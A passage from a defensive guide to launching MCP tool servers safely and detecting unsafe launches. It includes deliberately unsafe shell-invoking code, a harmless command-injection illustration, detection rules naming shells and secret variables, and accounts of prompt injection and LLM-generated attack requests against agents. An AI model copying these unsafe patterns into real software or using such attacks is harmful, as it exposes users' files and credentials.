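Hirschberg suggests that MCP adopt an approach like direnv's. When a developer enters a folder, direnv sets up their environment by running commands from a file called `.envrc`. When the developer approves the file, direnv records a hash of its content. Any edit changes the hash, so direnv requires approval again before running the file.

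The fix proposed for Claude Code's approval flaw would do the same for launch entries. The hash has to include the command, arguments, environment variables and working directory to cover every field that can change what runs.

| Change after Ana's approval | Approval by name | Approval by content |
|---|---|---|
| A colleague changes `command` to `date` | Runs without asking | Asks again |
| An agent adds a variable to `env` | Runs without asking | Asks again |
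| A publisher releases a new version of an unpinned package | Runs without asking | Runs without asking |
| A colleague rewrites a script that the entry names | Runs without asking | Runs without asking |

The last two rows need other protection, such as a pinned version or a separate hash of the script.

The host also has to hash either a placeholder's text or its value. If it hashes the text `${NOTES_DIR}`, someone can change the variable's value without triggering a new prompt. If it hashes the value, Ana has to approve the entry again whenever her folder's path changes. Hashing the value is worth the extra prompt when the placeholder supplies the program or a script's path.

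The host also has to keep its approvals outside the project, somewhere the agent can't write. Otherwise an attacker could supply a new entry and its approval together, as the malicious repositories did with Claude Code.

People who see the same dialog every day may stop reading it. Hashing the decoded values instead of the raw file would at least avoid prompting them over an added space or reordered fields.

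### What the project has changed since

After receiving OX Security's report, Anthropic updated its guidance to recommend caution with MCP adapters, especially those using stdio. According to ITPro, Anthropic also stressed that developers are responsible for securing their code. OX Security regards this as shifting the blame.

The Model Context Protocol's current guidance goes further than SEP-1024, but most of what it adds is recommended, not required. It recommends that host applications run local servers in a sandbox with limited access to files and the network, and let users grant more access when a server needs it. It also recommends highlighting suspicious commands, such as those containing `sudo`, which runs a program with administrator rights.

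The Model Context Protocol project's *Security Charter*, published in June 2026, sets up a group to study threats and refer problems to the people who write proposals. The group's scope includes the isolation of stdio processes and ways for a host to verify the programs it starts. The charter lists supply-chain integrity as an open topic with nobody assigned to lead it. Another open topic is what should happen when a server changes its tools after approval, which is related to a changed launch entry but is a separate problem.

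The Model Context Protocol specification of 28 July 2026 left the way servers are launched essentially unchanged. Its text on launching a server repeats *Transports* (2025) almost word for word, apart from the advice to restart a server that exits unexpectedly. The list of changes includes nothing about launch commands, consent or sandboxing, and the security changes concern signing in to remote servers.

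Kale (2026), in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential*, argues that the July specification moved security enforcement from the protocol to developers. For local launches, the protocol had little enforcement to move, because the host application already had to decide what was safe to run.

The next specification is due on 30 March 2027. Under a roadmap updated on 16 November (Model Context Protocol, 2026), local servers would still run as subprocesses but would exchange web-style messages over standard input and output. None of the roadmap's deliverables concerns approval of launch commands. Proposals outside its priority areas wait longer and must meet a higher standard, and anything meant for the March release must be final by about mid-January. The maintainers describe the roadmap as current thinking and not a commitment, but a new rule on local launches looks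 unlikely before the second half of 2027.

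## How should a tool server be launched?

A new rule on launches is unlikely before late 2027, so safe launching depends on the people who write launch entries and build host applications. They need to launch servers without a shell where they can, control which code each entry runs, and limit what that code can access.

### Taking the shell out of an entry

Suppose Ana's entry currently looks like this:

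```json
{
  "command": "bash",
  "args": ["-lc", "cd ~/'R&D notes' && NOTES_LOG=info notes-server ."]
}
```

The command works because Ana quoted the ampersand correctly. But bash runs her start-up files before every launch, and any output from them could break the MCP connection. She would also have to rework the quoting if she moved her notes to a folder with an apostrophe in its name.

Ana uses a login shell only so that bash can find notes-server. She can run `which notes-server` in a terminal (`where notes-server` on Windows) and use the full path it prints:

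```json
"command": "/usr/local/bin/notes-server"
```

Using the full path to the server's program prevents the `ENOENT` error that a limited search path causes, and avoids differences between systems. According to Python's *subprocess*, the working directory and a `PATH` value in `env` can change which program Python finds on Linux and macOS, but not on Windows. A full path doesn't help if an attacker can replace the file at that location.

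Next, Ana gives the folder its own string:

```json
"args": ["/home/ana/R&D notes"]
```

She leaves out the shell's quotation marks and writes out her home folder, since nothing will expand `~`. The folder's name can no longer cause command injection on Linux or macOS, though notes-server would still treat a folder named `--writable` as an option. A shell ignores an unquoted space at the end of a command, but direct invocation keeps it in the argument, so `"/home/ana/R&D notes "` refers to a different folder. Claude Code warns about whitespace at either end of a value but, according to Anthropic, doesn't remove it.

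`NOTES_LOG=info` in front of a command is shell syntax, so the setting moves to `env`:

```json
"env": { "NOTES_LOG": "info" }
```

A password also belongs in `env` rather than in `args`, but anyone who can read the configuration file can still read the password. Darinor's *How to Vet an MCP Server Before You Install It* (2026) cites a search by the security company GitGuardian that found over 24,000 secrets in MCP-related configuration files on public GitHub, 2,117 of them still valid. In a shared file, Ana should write a reference such as `${NOTES_KEY}`, if her host supports it, and set the value on her own machine.

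The `cwd` field replaces `cd`, which gives her this entry:

```json
{
  "command": "/usr/local/bin/notes-server",
  "args": ["/home/ana/R&D notes"],
  "env": { "NOTES_LOG": "info" },
  "cwd": "/home/ana/R&D notes"
}
```

The folder appears twice, as an argument and as `cwd`, because notes-server opens its working directory if no argument names a folder. With `cwd` set, a missing argument can't expose the rest of Ana's home folder. If a host has no `cwd` field, full paths are the best substitute. Claude Code also gives each local server the project's location in the `CLAUDE_PROJECT_DIR` variable.

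The same approach works for Python servers whose instructions begin by activating a virtual environment, a private set of Python packages. freeCodeCamp's *How to fix the Python ENOENT error when setting up MCP servers* puts the full path of the environment's Python in `command` and the server's script in `args`. That copy of Python loads the environment's packages without activation.

### Starting a Node.js server on Windows

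On Windows, `npx` and the commands that npm installs are usually batch files, so removing `cmd /c` from an entry doesn't remove cmd.exe from the launch. Ana can avoid the batch file by starting `node.exe` with the server's script:

```json
{
  "command": "C:\\Program Files\\nodejs\\node.exe",
  "args": [
    "C:\\Users\\Ana\\AppData\\Roaming\\npm\\node_modules\\notes-server\\dist\\index.js",
    "C:\\R&D"
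  ],
  "cwd": "C:\\R&D"
}
```

*Solution for MCP Servers Connection Issues with NVM/NPM* describes how to find the paths to `node.exe` and the package's script. The user installs the package globally, runs `where node` to find `node.exe`, and runs `npm root -g` to find the folder that holds installed packages. The `bin` field in the package's `package.json` gives the script's location within the package.

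Windows can start `node.exe` without cmd.exe, so only Node.js has to split the command line. The folder `C:\R&D`, which broke under `cmd /c npx`, then arrives intact, as does a folder with percent signs in its name. Escaping percent signs for cmd.exe is unreliable, and Sun (2017), in *Explain why it is recommended to pass args as a string*, found no way to do it on the command line.

This entry doesn't help if the host turns on Node's `shell` option, which runs the command through cmd.exe again. Ana would probably notice, because the space in `C:\Program Files` would cause the error `'C:\Program' is not recognized`.

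### When a setup step needs a shell

A short script can handle a step such as reading an access key from a file, provided that its text never changes and the folder arrives as an argument:

```sh
#!/bin/sh
set -eu
NOTES_KEY=$(cat /home/ana/.config/notes/key)
export NOTES_KEY
exec /usr/local/bin/notes-server -- "$1"
```

If Ana saves this as `/usr/local/bin/start-notes`, her entry becomes:

```json
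{
  "command": "/usr/local/bin/start-notes",
  "args": ["/home/ana/R&D notes"]
}
```

`set -eu` stops the script if it can't read the key file or if the entry supplies no folder. The script also passes on only one value, after `--`. If notes-server follows the usual convention for `--`, it will treat `--writable` as the name of a folder that doesn't exist. The earlier wrapper with `"$@"` didn't have this protection.

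Anyone who can edit the script can still run whatever they like, so it should be kept in a folder that neither the agent nor the project can write to. On Windows, a short Python or Node.js script is better than a batch file, as long as the entry starts it through `python.exe` or `node.exe`, because cmd.exe inserts arguments into a batch file's lines as text.

### Process calls for host developers

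A host application should keep the argument array intact all the way to the operating system. In these calls, `folder` is a value from outside the program:

| Language | Unsafe | Safe on Linux and macOS |
|---|---|---|
| Python | `Popen("notes-server " + folder, shell=True)` | `Popen(["/usr/local/bin/notes-server", "--", folder])` |
| Node.js | `exec("notes-server " + folder)` | `spawn("/usr/local/bin/notes-server", ["--", folder])` |
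| Node.js | `spawn("notes-server", [folder], { shell: true })` | `spawn("/usr/local/bin/notes-server", ["--", folder], { shell: false })` |

The safe calls also work on Windows if the program is an `.exe` file. They don't make a batch file safe.

OpenStack's *Use subprocess securely* makes the same correction to a Python function that runs the network utility `ping` on a user-supplied address. The corrected version doesn't check for a leading dash, though, so a user could still pass an option to `ping`.

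A host that uses an official kit can fill in the kit's fields instead of making these calls itself. In Python:

```python
StdioServerParameters(
    command="/usr/local/bin/notes-server",
    args=["--", folder],
    env={"NOTES_LOG": "info"},
    cwd=folder,
)
```

And in TypeScript:

```ts
new StdioClientTransport({
  command: "/usr/local/bin/notes-server",
  args: ["--", folder],
  env: { NOTES_LOG: "info" },
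  cwd: folder
})
```

Developers who start processes without a kit need to be careful with `env`. In Python, it replaces the whole inherited environment, and some Windows programs won't start unless it includes `SystemRoot`. In Node.js on Linux or macOS, an `env` without `PATH` limits the search for a bare program name to the default `/usr/bin:/bin`. On Windows, Node.js treats `PATH` and `Path` as the same variable and passes on only the one that sorts first, so merging two environments can discard the value the developer meant to keep.

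Direct invocation also gives clearer errors. Python raises an error at once if it can't find notes-server, whereas with `shell=True` the host has to check the exit status.

To convert an old command string, a developer can run Python's `shlex.split` once and save the list it returns. This works for `notes-server '/home/ana/R&D notes'`. But the function only splits text and doesn't carry out shell operations, so given `cd folder && npx notes-server`, it returns `cd` as the program and `&&` as an ordinary argument. Treating `cd` as a program caused the Shopify user's `spawn cd ENOENT` error.

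### Fixing the version of the package

None of these calls controls what is inside the package. Archestra's *Every 10th MCP server is one person* advises always giving `npx` an exact version:

```json
"args": ["-y", "notes-server@1.4.2", "/home/ana/R&D notes"]
```

The tag `latest` does not pin the package to one version, and a narrow version range is little better. Stacklok's *Examining the impact of npm supply chain attacks on MCP* points out that attackers have used patch releases, the smallest kind of update, which a range such as `~1.2.3` accepts automatically.

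Pinning a server to an exact version doesn't pin the packages it depends on, as tests by the security company Corelight showed. Zorz (2026), in *Your pinned MCP server may not be as pinned as you think*, reports that one server on an administrator's workstation ran with 15 different sets of dependencies in five weeks. Nobody had changed its launch entry, which named one exact release. Of the server's 69 packages, 23 changed version, including its cryptography library and the MCP kit.

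The workstation's AI assistants started their servers with `uvx`. One community server came with a lock file, which lists the exact version and hash of every dependency. `uvx` ignored this file and used the package's looser requirements, so it chose versions again from the public Python registry each time it rebuilt the environment.

An assistant started one server 162 times in a week, mostly from a cached environment, yet the cache still held 19 builds of the same release, roughly one every two days. Builds that frequent could install a hijacked package even if it is available for only minutes or hours before someone removes it. Corelight measured changed versions and did not measure infections.

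The risk was high on this machine because the servers held an administrator's credentials. In one week they made more than 1,600 connections to 11 management systems, including the firewall.

Corelight also reviewed 35 servers from two vendors' catalogues and its own lab. For 23 of them, the recommended installation would fetch dependencies from a public registry at each launch, installation or image build. The risks differ, because a server that fetches packages only at installation can't change between launches. The sample is too small and selective to give a rate for MCP servers in general.

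Corelight then froze the versions of five servers. For each one, it chose an exact commit (a recorded state of the source code), installed the server once from a lock file with hashes, launched it directly and turned off update checks. Over the next two weeks, the assistants started these servers 457 times, and the installed packages matched the original list every time.

Ana can do much the same with notes-server. After she downloads one commit to `/opt/notes-server`, the command `npm ci` installs the versions in its lock file. Adding `--ignore-scripts` stops packages from running their own commands during installation, though some packages need those commands to work. Once she has built the server, if its source needs building, her entry bypasses `npx`:

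```json
{
  "command": "/usr/bin/node",
  "args": ["/opt/notes-server/dist/index.js", "/home/ana/R&D notes"],
  "cwd": "/home/ana/R&D notes"
}
```

Frozen code goes out of date. When Corelight froze one community server, 40 of its packages were already older than the versions `uvx` would have fetched that day, and some of them affected security. The Shopify user similarly disliked running a local copy because it meant updating the server by hand.

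Pinning an old version can also leave a serious flaw in place. mcp-server-git has a `--repository` option meant to confine it to one project. *A nested .git file let the Git MCP server out of its …* (rulestack, 2026) reports that a nested `.git` file let the server escape that limit until version 2026.10.28. An entry pinned to an earlier version would still have the flaw.

A server pinned to a fixed version needs an update schedule. James Lagermann, who ran Corelight's tests, has the servers he maintains checked for vulnerabilities every night and updated the next morning if a check finds one. Most individual users won't do that, but they can at least subscribe to a server's security notices. Bishop Fox, a security company, recommends reviewing a package again before each update, because a clean history doesn't guarantee that the next release is safe. Docker does this for its catalogue by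 having AI agents examine the code changes before a person makes the final decision.

Pinning a tool server to one version won't help if that release was malicious from the start, which is a reason to limit what the server can access.

### Reducing the environment

A host often has access to passwords and keys that a tool server doesn't need. The launch code for OpenAI's Codex therefore passes on only environment variables considered safe. *feat*, the code change that introduced this restriction, explains that developers commonly keep sensitive API keys in their environment.

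The official TypeScript and Python kits also start from a short list of environment variables. A copy of the TypeScript code in Glama's *Codebase MCP* lists six for Linux and macOS: `HOME`, `LOGNAME`, `PATH`, `SHELL`, `TERM` and `USER`. If Ana has set a cloud access key in her terminal, notes-server doesn't inherit it unless she adds it to the entry. The C# kit passes on the host's whole environment unless the developer turns this off.

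A reduced environment protects keys that exist only in the environment. If Ana also stores the cloud key in a file in her home folder, notes-server can read it there because it runs with her permissions. A reduced environment is still worth having, but it needs file restrictions too.

### Running the server in a container

A container can restrict files and the network at the same time. With Docker, Ana's entry might be:

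```json
{
  "command": "/usr/bin/docker",
  "args": [
    "run", "--rm", "-i",
    "--network", "none",
    "--read-only",
    "--mount", "type=bind,source=/home/ana/R&D notes,target=/notes,readonly",
    "notes-image@sha256:<digest>",
    "/notes"
  ]
}
```

The `-i` option keeps standard input open for MCP messages. The `--mount` option gives the container read-only access to Ana's notes at `/notes`. `<digest>` stands for the hash of one exact image. The image includes the server's dependencies, so specifying its hash also prevents the changes that Corelight saw between launches. The entry relies on the image starting notes-server from a list, without a shell.

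Docker still splits the `--mount` value at commas, so a folder called "R&D notes" works, but one called "R,D notes" would need Docker's own quoting.

notes-server can now read the notes but can't reach the rest of Ana's files or open a network connection. Every exception she adds gives back some of that access:

| What Ana passes into the container | What remains exposed |
|---|---|
| Her notes, read-only | Every note, since the server can return its text to the model |
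| A project folder, with write access | The source code, plus launch entries, editor tasks and git hooks that may later run outside the container |
| An access key | Everything the key permits on any service the container can reach |
| Her home folder | Most of what the container was meant to protect |
| Docker's control socket | The whole machine, because the server can start another container with more access |

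The notes can still leak when the container's network is off, because the server can return a note containing a prompt injection, and the agent may then use a different tool to send the notes elsewhere. A server that needs the internet can't use `--network none`, so ideally its container would allow connections only to the addresses it needs.

A tool server's credentials also need limits. dbt tells administrators to control its tool for running database queries through the database's own permissions, because whoever configures the client can change the connection settings that disable the tool. If notes-server needs a database, a read-only account will limit the damage even if the container fails to isolate the server.

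An entry like Ana's protects her from notes-server, but not from someone who controls the launch command. That person can remove `--network none`, mount her home folder or replace `docker` with `date`. The host should therefore apply the restrictions outside the entry, or a separate manager can do so. *ToolHive* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes one such manager, an open-source tool from Stacklok that runs every MCP server in its own container.

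Archestra suggests a separate user account or a virtual machine as alternatives to a container. A separate account is simple and keeps the server out of Ana's private files if their permissions exclude other users. It doesn't restrict the server's network access. A virtual machine usually gives stronger separation than a container because it runs its own operating system kernel, but it needs more memory and setup.

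Limits that a server places on itself offer weaker protection. The Coalition for Secure AI's *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Security* (2026) recommends sandboxing against command injection and mentions support for roots, an MCP feature that lets a host give a server a list of folders to use. Roots help a server that follows the list stay within those folders, but a malicious server can ignore it. A server can also fail to enforce its own limit by mistake, as mcp-server-git did with its faulty `--repository` check.

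### Keeping the agent out of the configuration

If the agent can edit its launch entries, an attacker may be able to undo all of this through prompt injection. The simplest protection is to keep the entries in a file that an administrator owns and the agent's account can only read. On Linux and macOS, the folder needs the same protection. Otherwise the agent could rename the file and put a new one in its place.

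The agent also shouldn't be able to modify any script, package or image definition that an entry uses. Making an entry that starts `/home/ana/project/server.js` read-only gives little protection if the agent can rewrite `server.js`. An agent that can run shell commands outside a sandbox can start programs without a launch entry, so write protection has to be combined with limits on the agent's other tools.

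Some hosts write to their own configuration files, so making those files read-only is impractical. Claude Code, for example, keeps a user's personal entries in `~/.claude.json` along with other settings. An administrator can supply a managed configuration instead. A colleague can't change personal entries by editing the repository, as they can with a project's shared `.mcp.json`. But if both files define a server with the same name, Claude Code uses the personal entry only if the user added it for that project alone. If the user added it for all projects, the shared entry takes its place.

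Claude Code now also ignores a project's attempt to approve its own servers if the user hasn't trusted the folder. But when it runs without an interactive session, through `claude -p`, it loads the project's servers without asking. An automated job can avoid this by naming its own configuration:

```
claude -p "Summarise the notes" --strict-mcp-config --mcp-config /etc/notes/mcp.json
```

Claude Code then skips the servers in `.mcp.json`. The `disabledMcpjsonServers` setting blocks individual servers by name, which is less reliable against an attacker, who can choose another name.

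### Checklist

For a launch entry:

- `command` is the full path of the server or its interpreter, not a shell or a package runner.
- Each argument is a separate string, with no quotation marks for a shell.
- Settings are in `env`, and shared files contain references instead of passwords.
- `cwd` is the narrowest folder that works.
- On Windows, a Node.js server starts through `node.exe`.
- A lock file or image digest fixes the server and its dependencies, and someone is responsible for updates.

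For a host application:

- The launch code passes an argument array and leaves the shell option off.
- Values from outside can't become options or choose the code that runs.
- The server inherits only the environment variables it needs.
- The host applies file and network limits that the launch entry can't remove.
- The agent can't write to the launch entries or the files they run.

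## How are unsafe launches found?

Ana can go through the checklist by hand because she has one launch entry, but a company with hundreds of laptops needs software to do it. That software can examine configuration files, source code or running programs, and what it can find depends heavily on which it examines.

### Checking launch entries

A configuration check reads launch entries without starting anything. Five simple rules catch many of the faults that are visible in the text:

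1. `command` names a shell, such as `sh`, `bash`, `cmd` or `powershell`.
2. An argument is an option that takes a command string or program text, such as `-c`, `-lc`, `/c` or `--eval`.
3. An argument contains a character with a special meaning to a shell, such as `&`, `;`, `|` or `$`.
4. A package runner fetches a package without an exact version.
5. A variable whose name contains `KEY`, `TOKEN` or `PASSWORD` holds a value instead of a reference.

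Here is a sound entry for notes-server:

```json
{
  "command": "/usr/local/bin/notes-server",
  "args": ["/home/ana/R&D notes"],
  "env": { "NOTES_KEY": "${NOTES_KEY}" }
}
```

This one is unsound:

```json
{
  "command": "sh",
  "args": ["-c", "npx -y notes-server /home/ana/R&D notes"],
  "env": { "NOTES_KEY": "blue-sky-7" }
}
```

And this is a legitimate entry for Windows, in the form that Spring AI recommends:

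```json
{
  "command": "cmd",
  "args": ["/c", "npx", "-y", "notes-server@1.4.2", "C:\\notes"]
}
```

| Rule | Sound entry | Unsound entry | `cmd /c npx` entry |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shell as the command | Passes | Alarm | False alarm |
| Option that takes a command string | Passes | Alarm | False alarm |
| Special character in an argument | False alarm | Alarm | Passes |
| Package without an exact version | Passes | Missed, unless the check also reads the command string | Passes |
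| Secret in plain text | Passes | Alarm | Passes |

The Windows entry matches two rules even though the launch works. If Ana changed the folder to `C:\R&D`, the launch would break and the third rule would match too. A check could therefore treat `cmd /c` with a package runner as a minor warning and raise an alarm only if an argument also contains a special character.

Applying the third rule only where a shell is likely would remove the false alarm on the safe entry. A shell is likely when an entry matches one of the first two rules or, on Windows, starts a batch file. A project's shared file may be used on several systems, so a cautious check would assume Windows.

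All five rules miss the harmless stand-in for an attacker who controls the launch command:

```json
{ "command": "date", "args": [] }
```

To catch an unsafe launch, a check has to compare each entry in the configuration file with a list of approved entries. Even then, the file doesn't show whether the host application enables a shell option in its own code.

*A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025) gives some evidence of how often the fifth rule would find something. It describes a search of 5,659 example configurations on the registry mcp.so that found nine GitHub access tokens, five of which still worked in July 2025. Some developers had misunderstood a template on the site and filled in their own tokens, which could let a stranger rewrite their servers' code. People wrote these examples for publication, so private configuration files probably contain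 more secrets.

Evidence on the other rules is thinner. Products that read MCP configurations often look for problems other than unsafe launch commands. Rostamzadeh and colleagues describe one, MCP-Scan, as searching for prompt injection, malicious tool descriptions and tools that change after approval. A clean result from such a product doesn't mean an entry is free of `sh -c`. *Agent Smith in Action* (Zha, Li and colleagues, 2026) compared five detectors on the same 100 tool servers but left out two configuration scanners because they examine how a server is deployed, not its source code.

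### Following outside input through source code

Taint analysis traces outside input through a program to a dangerous call. It needs a list of sources, where outside input enters, and a list of sinks, the calls that are dangerous if such input reaches them. In the unsafe version of notes-server's search tool, the source is the model's search term and the sink is `exec`:

```ts
const term = args.term            // source: the model supplies this
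const line = `grep -r ${term}`    // line now contains outside input
exec(line)                        // sink: a shell reads line
```

The analyser marks `term` as tainted, then marks `line` because it contains `term`, and reports a flaw when `line` reaches `exec`. If the code first passes `term` through a function that the analyser recognises as making it safe, the analyser removes the mark. A plain text search for `exec` would also flag `exec("date")`, which no outsider can influence.

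The analyser never runs the program, so it can cover code that nobody has tested. But it may report a path that can't occur in practice or that is blocked by a check it doesn't recognise.

### VIPER-MCP

*VIPER-MCP* (Sun, Kang and colleagues, 2026) tried to remove such false alarms by carrying out each suspected attack. The system covers command injection and two other flaws: path traversal, which lets an attacker reach files outside the permitted folder, and a flaw that lets an attacker make a server send web requests to addresses they choose.

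The first phase is taint analysis in two passes. The first pass treats every parameter of a tool handler as a source and looks for paths from it to a sink. For command injection, the sinks are 14 process-starting calls in JavaScript and TypeScript and 57 in Python. The second pass finds the function that encloses each suspicious path, which identifies the tool a model would have to call.

In the second phase, a language model writes four differently worded requests meant to make an agent call that tool with a harmful argument. The agent runs each request against a live copy of the server, where added code records whether the argument reaches the sink. Another model gives each attempt two scores from 0 to 10, one for whether the agent chose the right tool and one for how far the argument got. The system rewords the request if the agent chose the wrong tool, or changes the argument if the tool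 was right but the argument failed. It then repeats the process with the most promising attempts.

This second phase can take repeated attempts. A server called context-sync inserted a file path into a shell command, but the agent kept turning the test value into a harmless path. The injected command ran with a visible effect only after eight rounds. Someone who tried it once or twice might have wrongly concluded that the server was safe.

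Sun and colleagues ran the system on 39,884 public repositories and confirmed 106 previously unknown vulnerabilities, each with an observable effect. The flaws have received 67 CVE numbers so far, about half of them for command injection. The analysis took an average of 15 minutes per server in a sample of 500.

They also tested the system against two other scanners on 130 vulnerable servers and 130 that two experts had judged free of these flaws:

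| Scanner | False alarms among 130 sound servers | Misses among 130 vulnerable servers |
|---|---:|---:|
| VIPER-MCP | 0 (0%) | 10 (7.7%) |
| MCPSafetyScanner | 56 (43.1%) | 83 (63.8%) |
| Cisco's MCP scanner | 32 (24.6%) | 95 (73.1%) |

VIPER-MCP's overall miss rate is misleadingly low, because the system itself had found the flaws in 67 of the 130 vulnerable servers. Sun and colleagues attribute all ten misses to kinds of flaw it doesn't cover, such as SQL injection. Its own finds can't include those, so the misses must all be among the other 63 servers, where the miss rate is about 16%. The result on sound servers is more convincing, though zero false alarms in 130 servers is still compatible with a true rate of around 2%.

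The results also depend on the language model used. When Claude Haiku 4.5 wrote and scored the attacks, the system triggered flaws in at most two of the vulnerable servers, because the model refused to produce attack requests. With GPT-5.4-mini in that role, the system triggered flaws in up to 88. A scan may therefore find nothing on a vulnerable server because the model refused to write the attacks.

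VIPER-MCP handles only JavaScript, TypeScript and Python, and it has to start each server in isolation, which fails if the server depends on an outside service. It also ignores tools whose purpose is to run commands.

### Can taint analysis find an unsafe launch?

VIPER-MCP traces tool arguments but not launch settings, because Sun and colleagues exclude "deployment configurations". The system could find the `grep` flaw in notes-server, but it could not find an `sh -c` entry that starts notes-server, or the flaw in a platform such as WeKnora that runs whatever command a user submits.

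The same method could cover launches if someone chose different sources and sinks. On a hosted platform, the source would be a web request and the sink would be the kit's launch settings:

```python
entry = await request.json()     # source: a user supplies this
StdioServerParameters(
    command=entry["command"],    # sink: the kit will run this
    args=entry["args"],
)
```

Some unsafe launches would still be difficult for an analyser to find. WeKnora, for example, saved the launch entry in its database during one request and started the program during another, so an analyser can easily lose track of the value in between. To catch this, it would have to treat everything read from that database as outside input, which would produce more false alarms.

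Taint analysis would flag every code editor that supports local servers, because it would trace data from the user's configuration file to the launch, and these editors are designed to work that way. The trace doesn't show whether the user approved the entry, which is what matters in this case.

### Flaws that need two tools

Ordinary taint analysis follows only connections in the code, but an agent can connect tools itself. Zha and colleagues describe a server with one tool that writes files and another that runs commands but refuses dangerous ones. An attacker can have the agent write a forbidden command into a script with the first tool and run the script with the second. Neither tool's code calls the other, so the analyser finds no path between them.

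Their system, SCAN-MCP, asks a language model about each pair of tools on a server: could the first produce something that the second uses? It then checks the suggested chains against fixed rules. Zha and colleagues tried to reproduce every detector's reports in an isolated virtual machine, counting flaws of all kinds:

| Detector | Reports | Confirmed | Share confirmed |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| SCAN-MCP | 150 | 124 | 83% |
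| Language model alone | 126 | 64 | 51% |
| Tencent's A.I.G | 191 | 70 | 37% |
| Semgrep | 141 | 27 | 19% |
| Cisco's mcp-scanner | 2 | 0 | 0% |

Semgrep is a widely used scanner that searches code for patterns described in rules. An unconfirmed report may still be correct, since confirming some of SCAN-MCP's reports required a login or a storage service that wasn't available in the test.

The table doesn't show how many flaws each detector missed. A.I.G found 43 confirmed flaws in single tools that SCAN-MCP missed. When Zha and colleagues switched off SCAN-MCP's filters, they confirmed 44 more flaws but had to review 519 reports instead of 150. A small team might reasonably prefer the filtered list, even though it is incomplete.

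Of the 124 confirmed flaws, 19 took more than one tool to trigger. In follow-up tests, calling only the last tool reproduced none of those 19, so reviewing each tool separately could easily have missed them.

Analyzing source code also requires access to it. *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* (Zhang, Hu and colleagues, 2026) found that 3,007 of the 18,770 servers in the official MCP registry (16%) offered a remote connection but neither a package nor a link to source code.

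### How common are injection flaws in tool servers?

Published figures run from about 1% to 43%, mostly because they count different things.

The most widely repeated figure is 43%. Practical DevSecOps, a training company, gives it as the share of "tested MCP servers" vulnerable to command injection and dates the assessment to "2025–Feb 2026". The figure comes from Equixly's *MCP Servers* (2025), a March 2025 blog post about a month of tests on "some of the most popular" servers. In the post, Equixly doesn't say how many servers it tested or how it confirmed a flaw. The percentages for its four categories, 43%, 30%, 22% and 5%, add up to 100%. A server can have several flaws, so shares of servers would add up to 100% only by coincidence. The 43% may instead be a share of the flaws found, in which case the number of vulnerable servers is unknown.

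| Source | Sample | What it counted | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Equixly | Popular servers, number not given | Command injection, with no stated test | 43% |
| Kennedy | 2,614 implementations | Use of calls related to command injection | 34% |
| Enkrypt AI | Over 1,000 servers | Shell commands built from unsanitised input | 28% |
| *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* | Servers in four registries | Tools with a code flaw that Semgrep flagged | 1.2% to 4.44%, depending on the registry |
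| Oliveira and Fiser | 2,287 flaws reported by AI | Exploitable flaws of any kind, confirmed by hand | 4.1% of the reports |

*Classic Vulnerabilities Meet AI Infrastructure* (Kennedy, 2026) reports a figure from the security company Endor Labs that 34% of servers use risky calls. That figure might include a server that starts `grep` safely, with an argument array. Enkrypt AI, which sells a scanner for tool servers, uses a stricter definition that requires unsanitised input, and reports a lower figure.

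In the two studies at the bottom of the table, people checked at least some of the results. For *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, researchers read the code of 41 flagged servers and agreed with the scanner on 37. That is far better than Semgrep's 19% in Zha and colleagues' test, but Zha and colleagues required the attack to work, whereas *A First Look* kept only flaws inside a tool and accepted one if the code showed an unchecked path to a dangerous call. The percentages in *A First Look* are also uncertain, because it divides the number of flagged servers by the number of what it calls "extracted tools".

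For *Hunt Them All*, Oliveira and Fiser of the security company Trend Micro used an AI agent that reported 17,558 flaws in about 19,000 repositories. A second check reduced these to just over 15,000. They took a random sample of 2,287, had another model examine it, and reviewed by hand the 438 flaws that this model kept. Only 93 were exploitable. Of those, 22.5% allowed remote code execution, often through a wrapper around a command-line program.

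They then applied the 4.1% to the 19,000 repositories and estimated that about 770 were vulnerable (range 600 to 1,650). But 4.1% is a share of reported flaws, not of repositories. Taking 4.1% of the 15,000 reports it came from gives roughly 610 flaws, and some repositories had more than one. The estimate could still be too low, since nobody reviewed the 1,849 reports that the last model discarded.

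VIPER-MCP found 106 flaws in 39,884 repositories, or fewer than three per 1,000. This is a minimum because it counts only three kinds of flaw, and only where the system could start the server and make an attack work.

Counts of published vulnerabilities reflect what people have reported, not how many servers are affected. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) identified 24 MCP vulnerabilities with CVE numbers up to February 2026, of which seven (29%) were command injection. VIPER-MCP alone has since added 67 CVE numbers, so the share of each type depends heavily on who is looking and for what. *Exposed by Design* (2026) reports 68 vulnerabilities from live tests of servers on the public internet, so it doesn't cover the local servers that a host application starts itself.

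For someone choosing a public tool server, a few percent is a better-supported estimate of the exploitable flaw rate than 43%. But none of these studies measured how many launch entries are unsafe, and a server with no flaws in its code can still have an entry that passes its folder path through a shell.

### Watching configuration files

Monitoring can catch changes made after a scan. The simplest method is to compare each launch entry with an approved copy whenever the file changes, and send an alert if they differ. If a colleague or an agent replaces `notes-server` with `date`, this comparison detects the change, which the five rules miss.

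The monitor should compare the decoded entries, not the whole file. Some files, like Claude Code's `~/.claude.json`, also hold other settings, and an alert on every write would soon become a nuisance. On Windows and macOS, the monitor also has to ignore capitalisation in file names. Otherwise, a change to `MCP.json` could bypass it, as such a change bypassed Cursor's check.

An alert may come too late to prevent the launch. In the attacks on Cursor and Windsurf, the new entry ran as soon as the agent saved it. An administrator could still use the alert to identify which computer to investigate and which passwords to replace.

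File monitoring misses changes to the package or script that a launch entry runs, as does approval tied to the entry's content. A platform that stores launch entries in a database needs to monitor the database instead.

### Watching processes

An unsafe launch ends with the operating system starting a program, so security software can watch what an AI application starts. An obvious rule is to raise an alarm when the application starts a shell. On Ana's computer, an ordinary morning might look like this:

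```
code-editor
├── notes-server "/home/ana/R&D notes"
│   └── grep -r -- budget
├── bash -c "npm test"
└── bash -c "git status"
```

Both shells are harmless. The agent is running the project's tests and checking which files have changed, which a coding agent may do hundreds of times a day. Ordinary tool servers launched by Zed, or with `npx` on Windows, would also set off the rule. People who get that many false alarms tend to turn it off.

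The rule would also miss an entry that names `date`, because the editor starts that program without a shell. A monitor that compares the editor's child processes with the approved launch entries would catch that launch, if it can distinguish tool servers from programs the agent starts in a terminal.

It is more useful to watch what each tool server starts. The safe version of notes-server runs `grep` directly and never needs a shell, so this would be a good reason for an alarm:

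```
notes-server "/home/ana/R&D notes"
└── sh -c "grep -r budget; date"
    └── date
```

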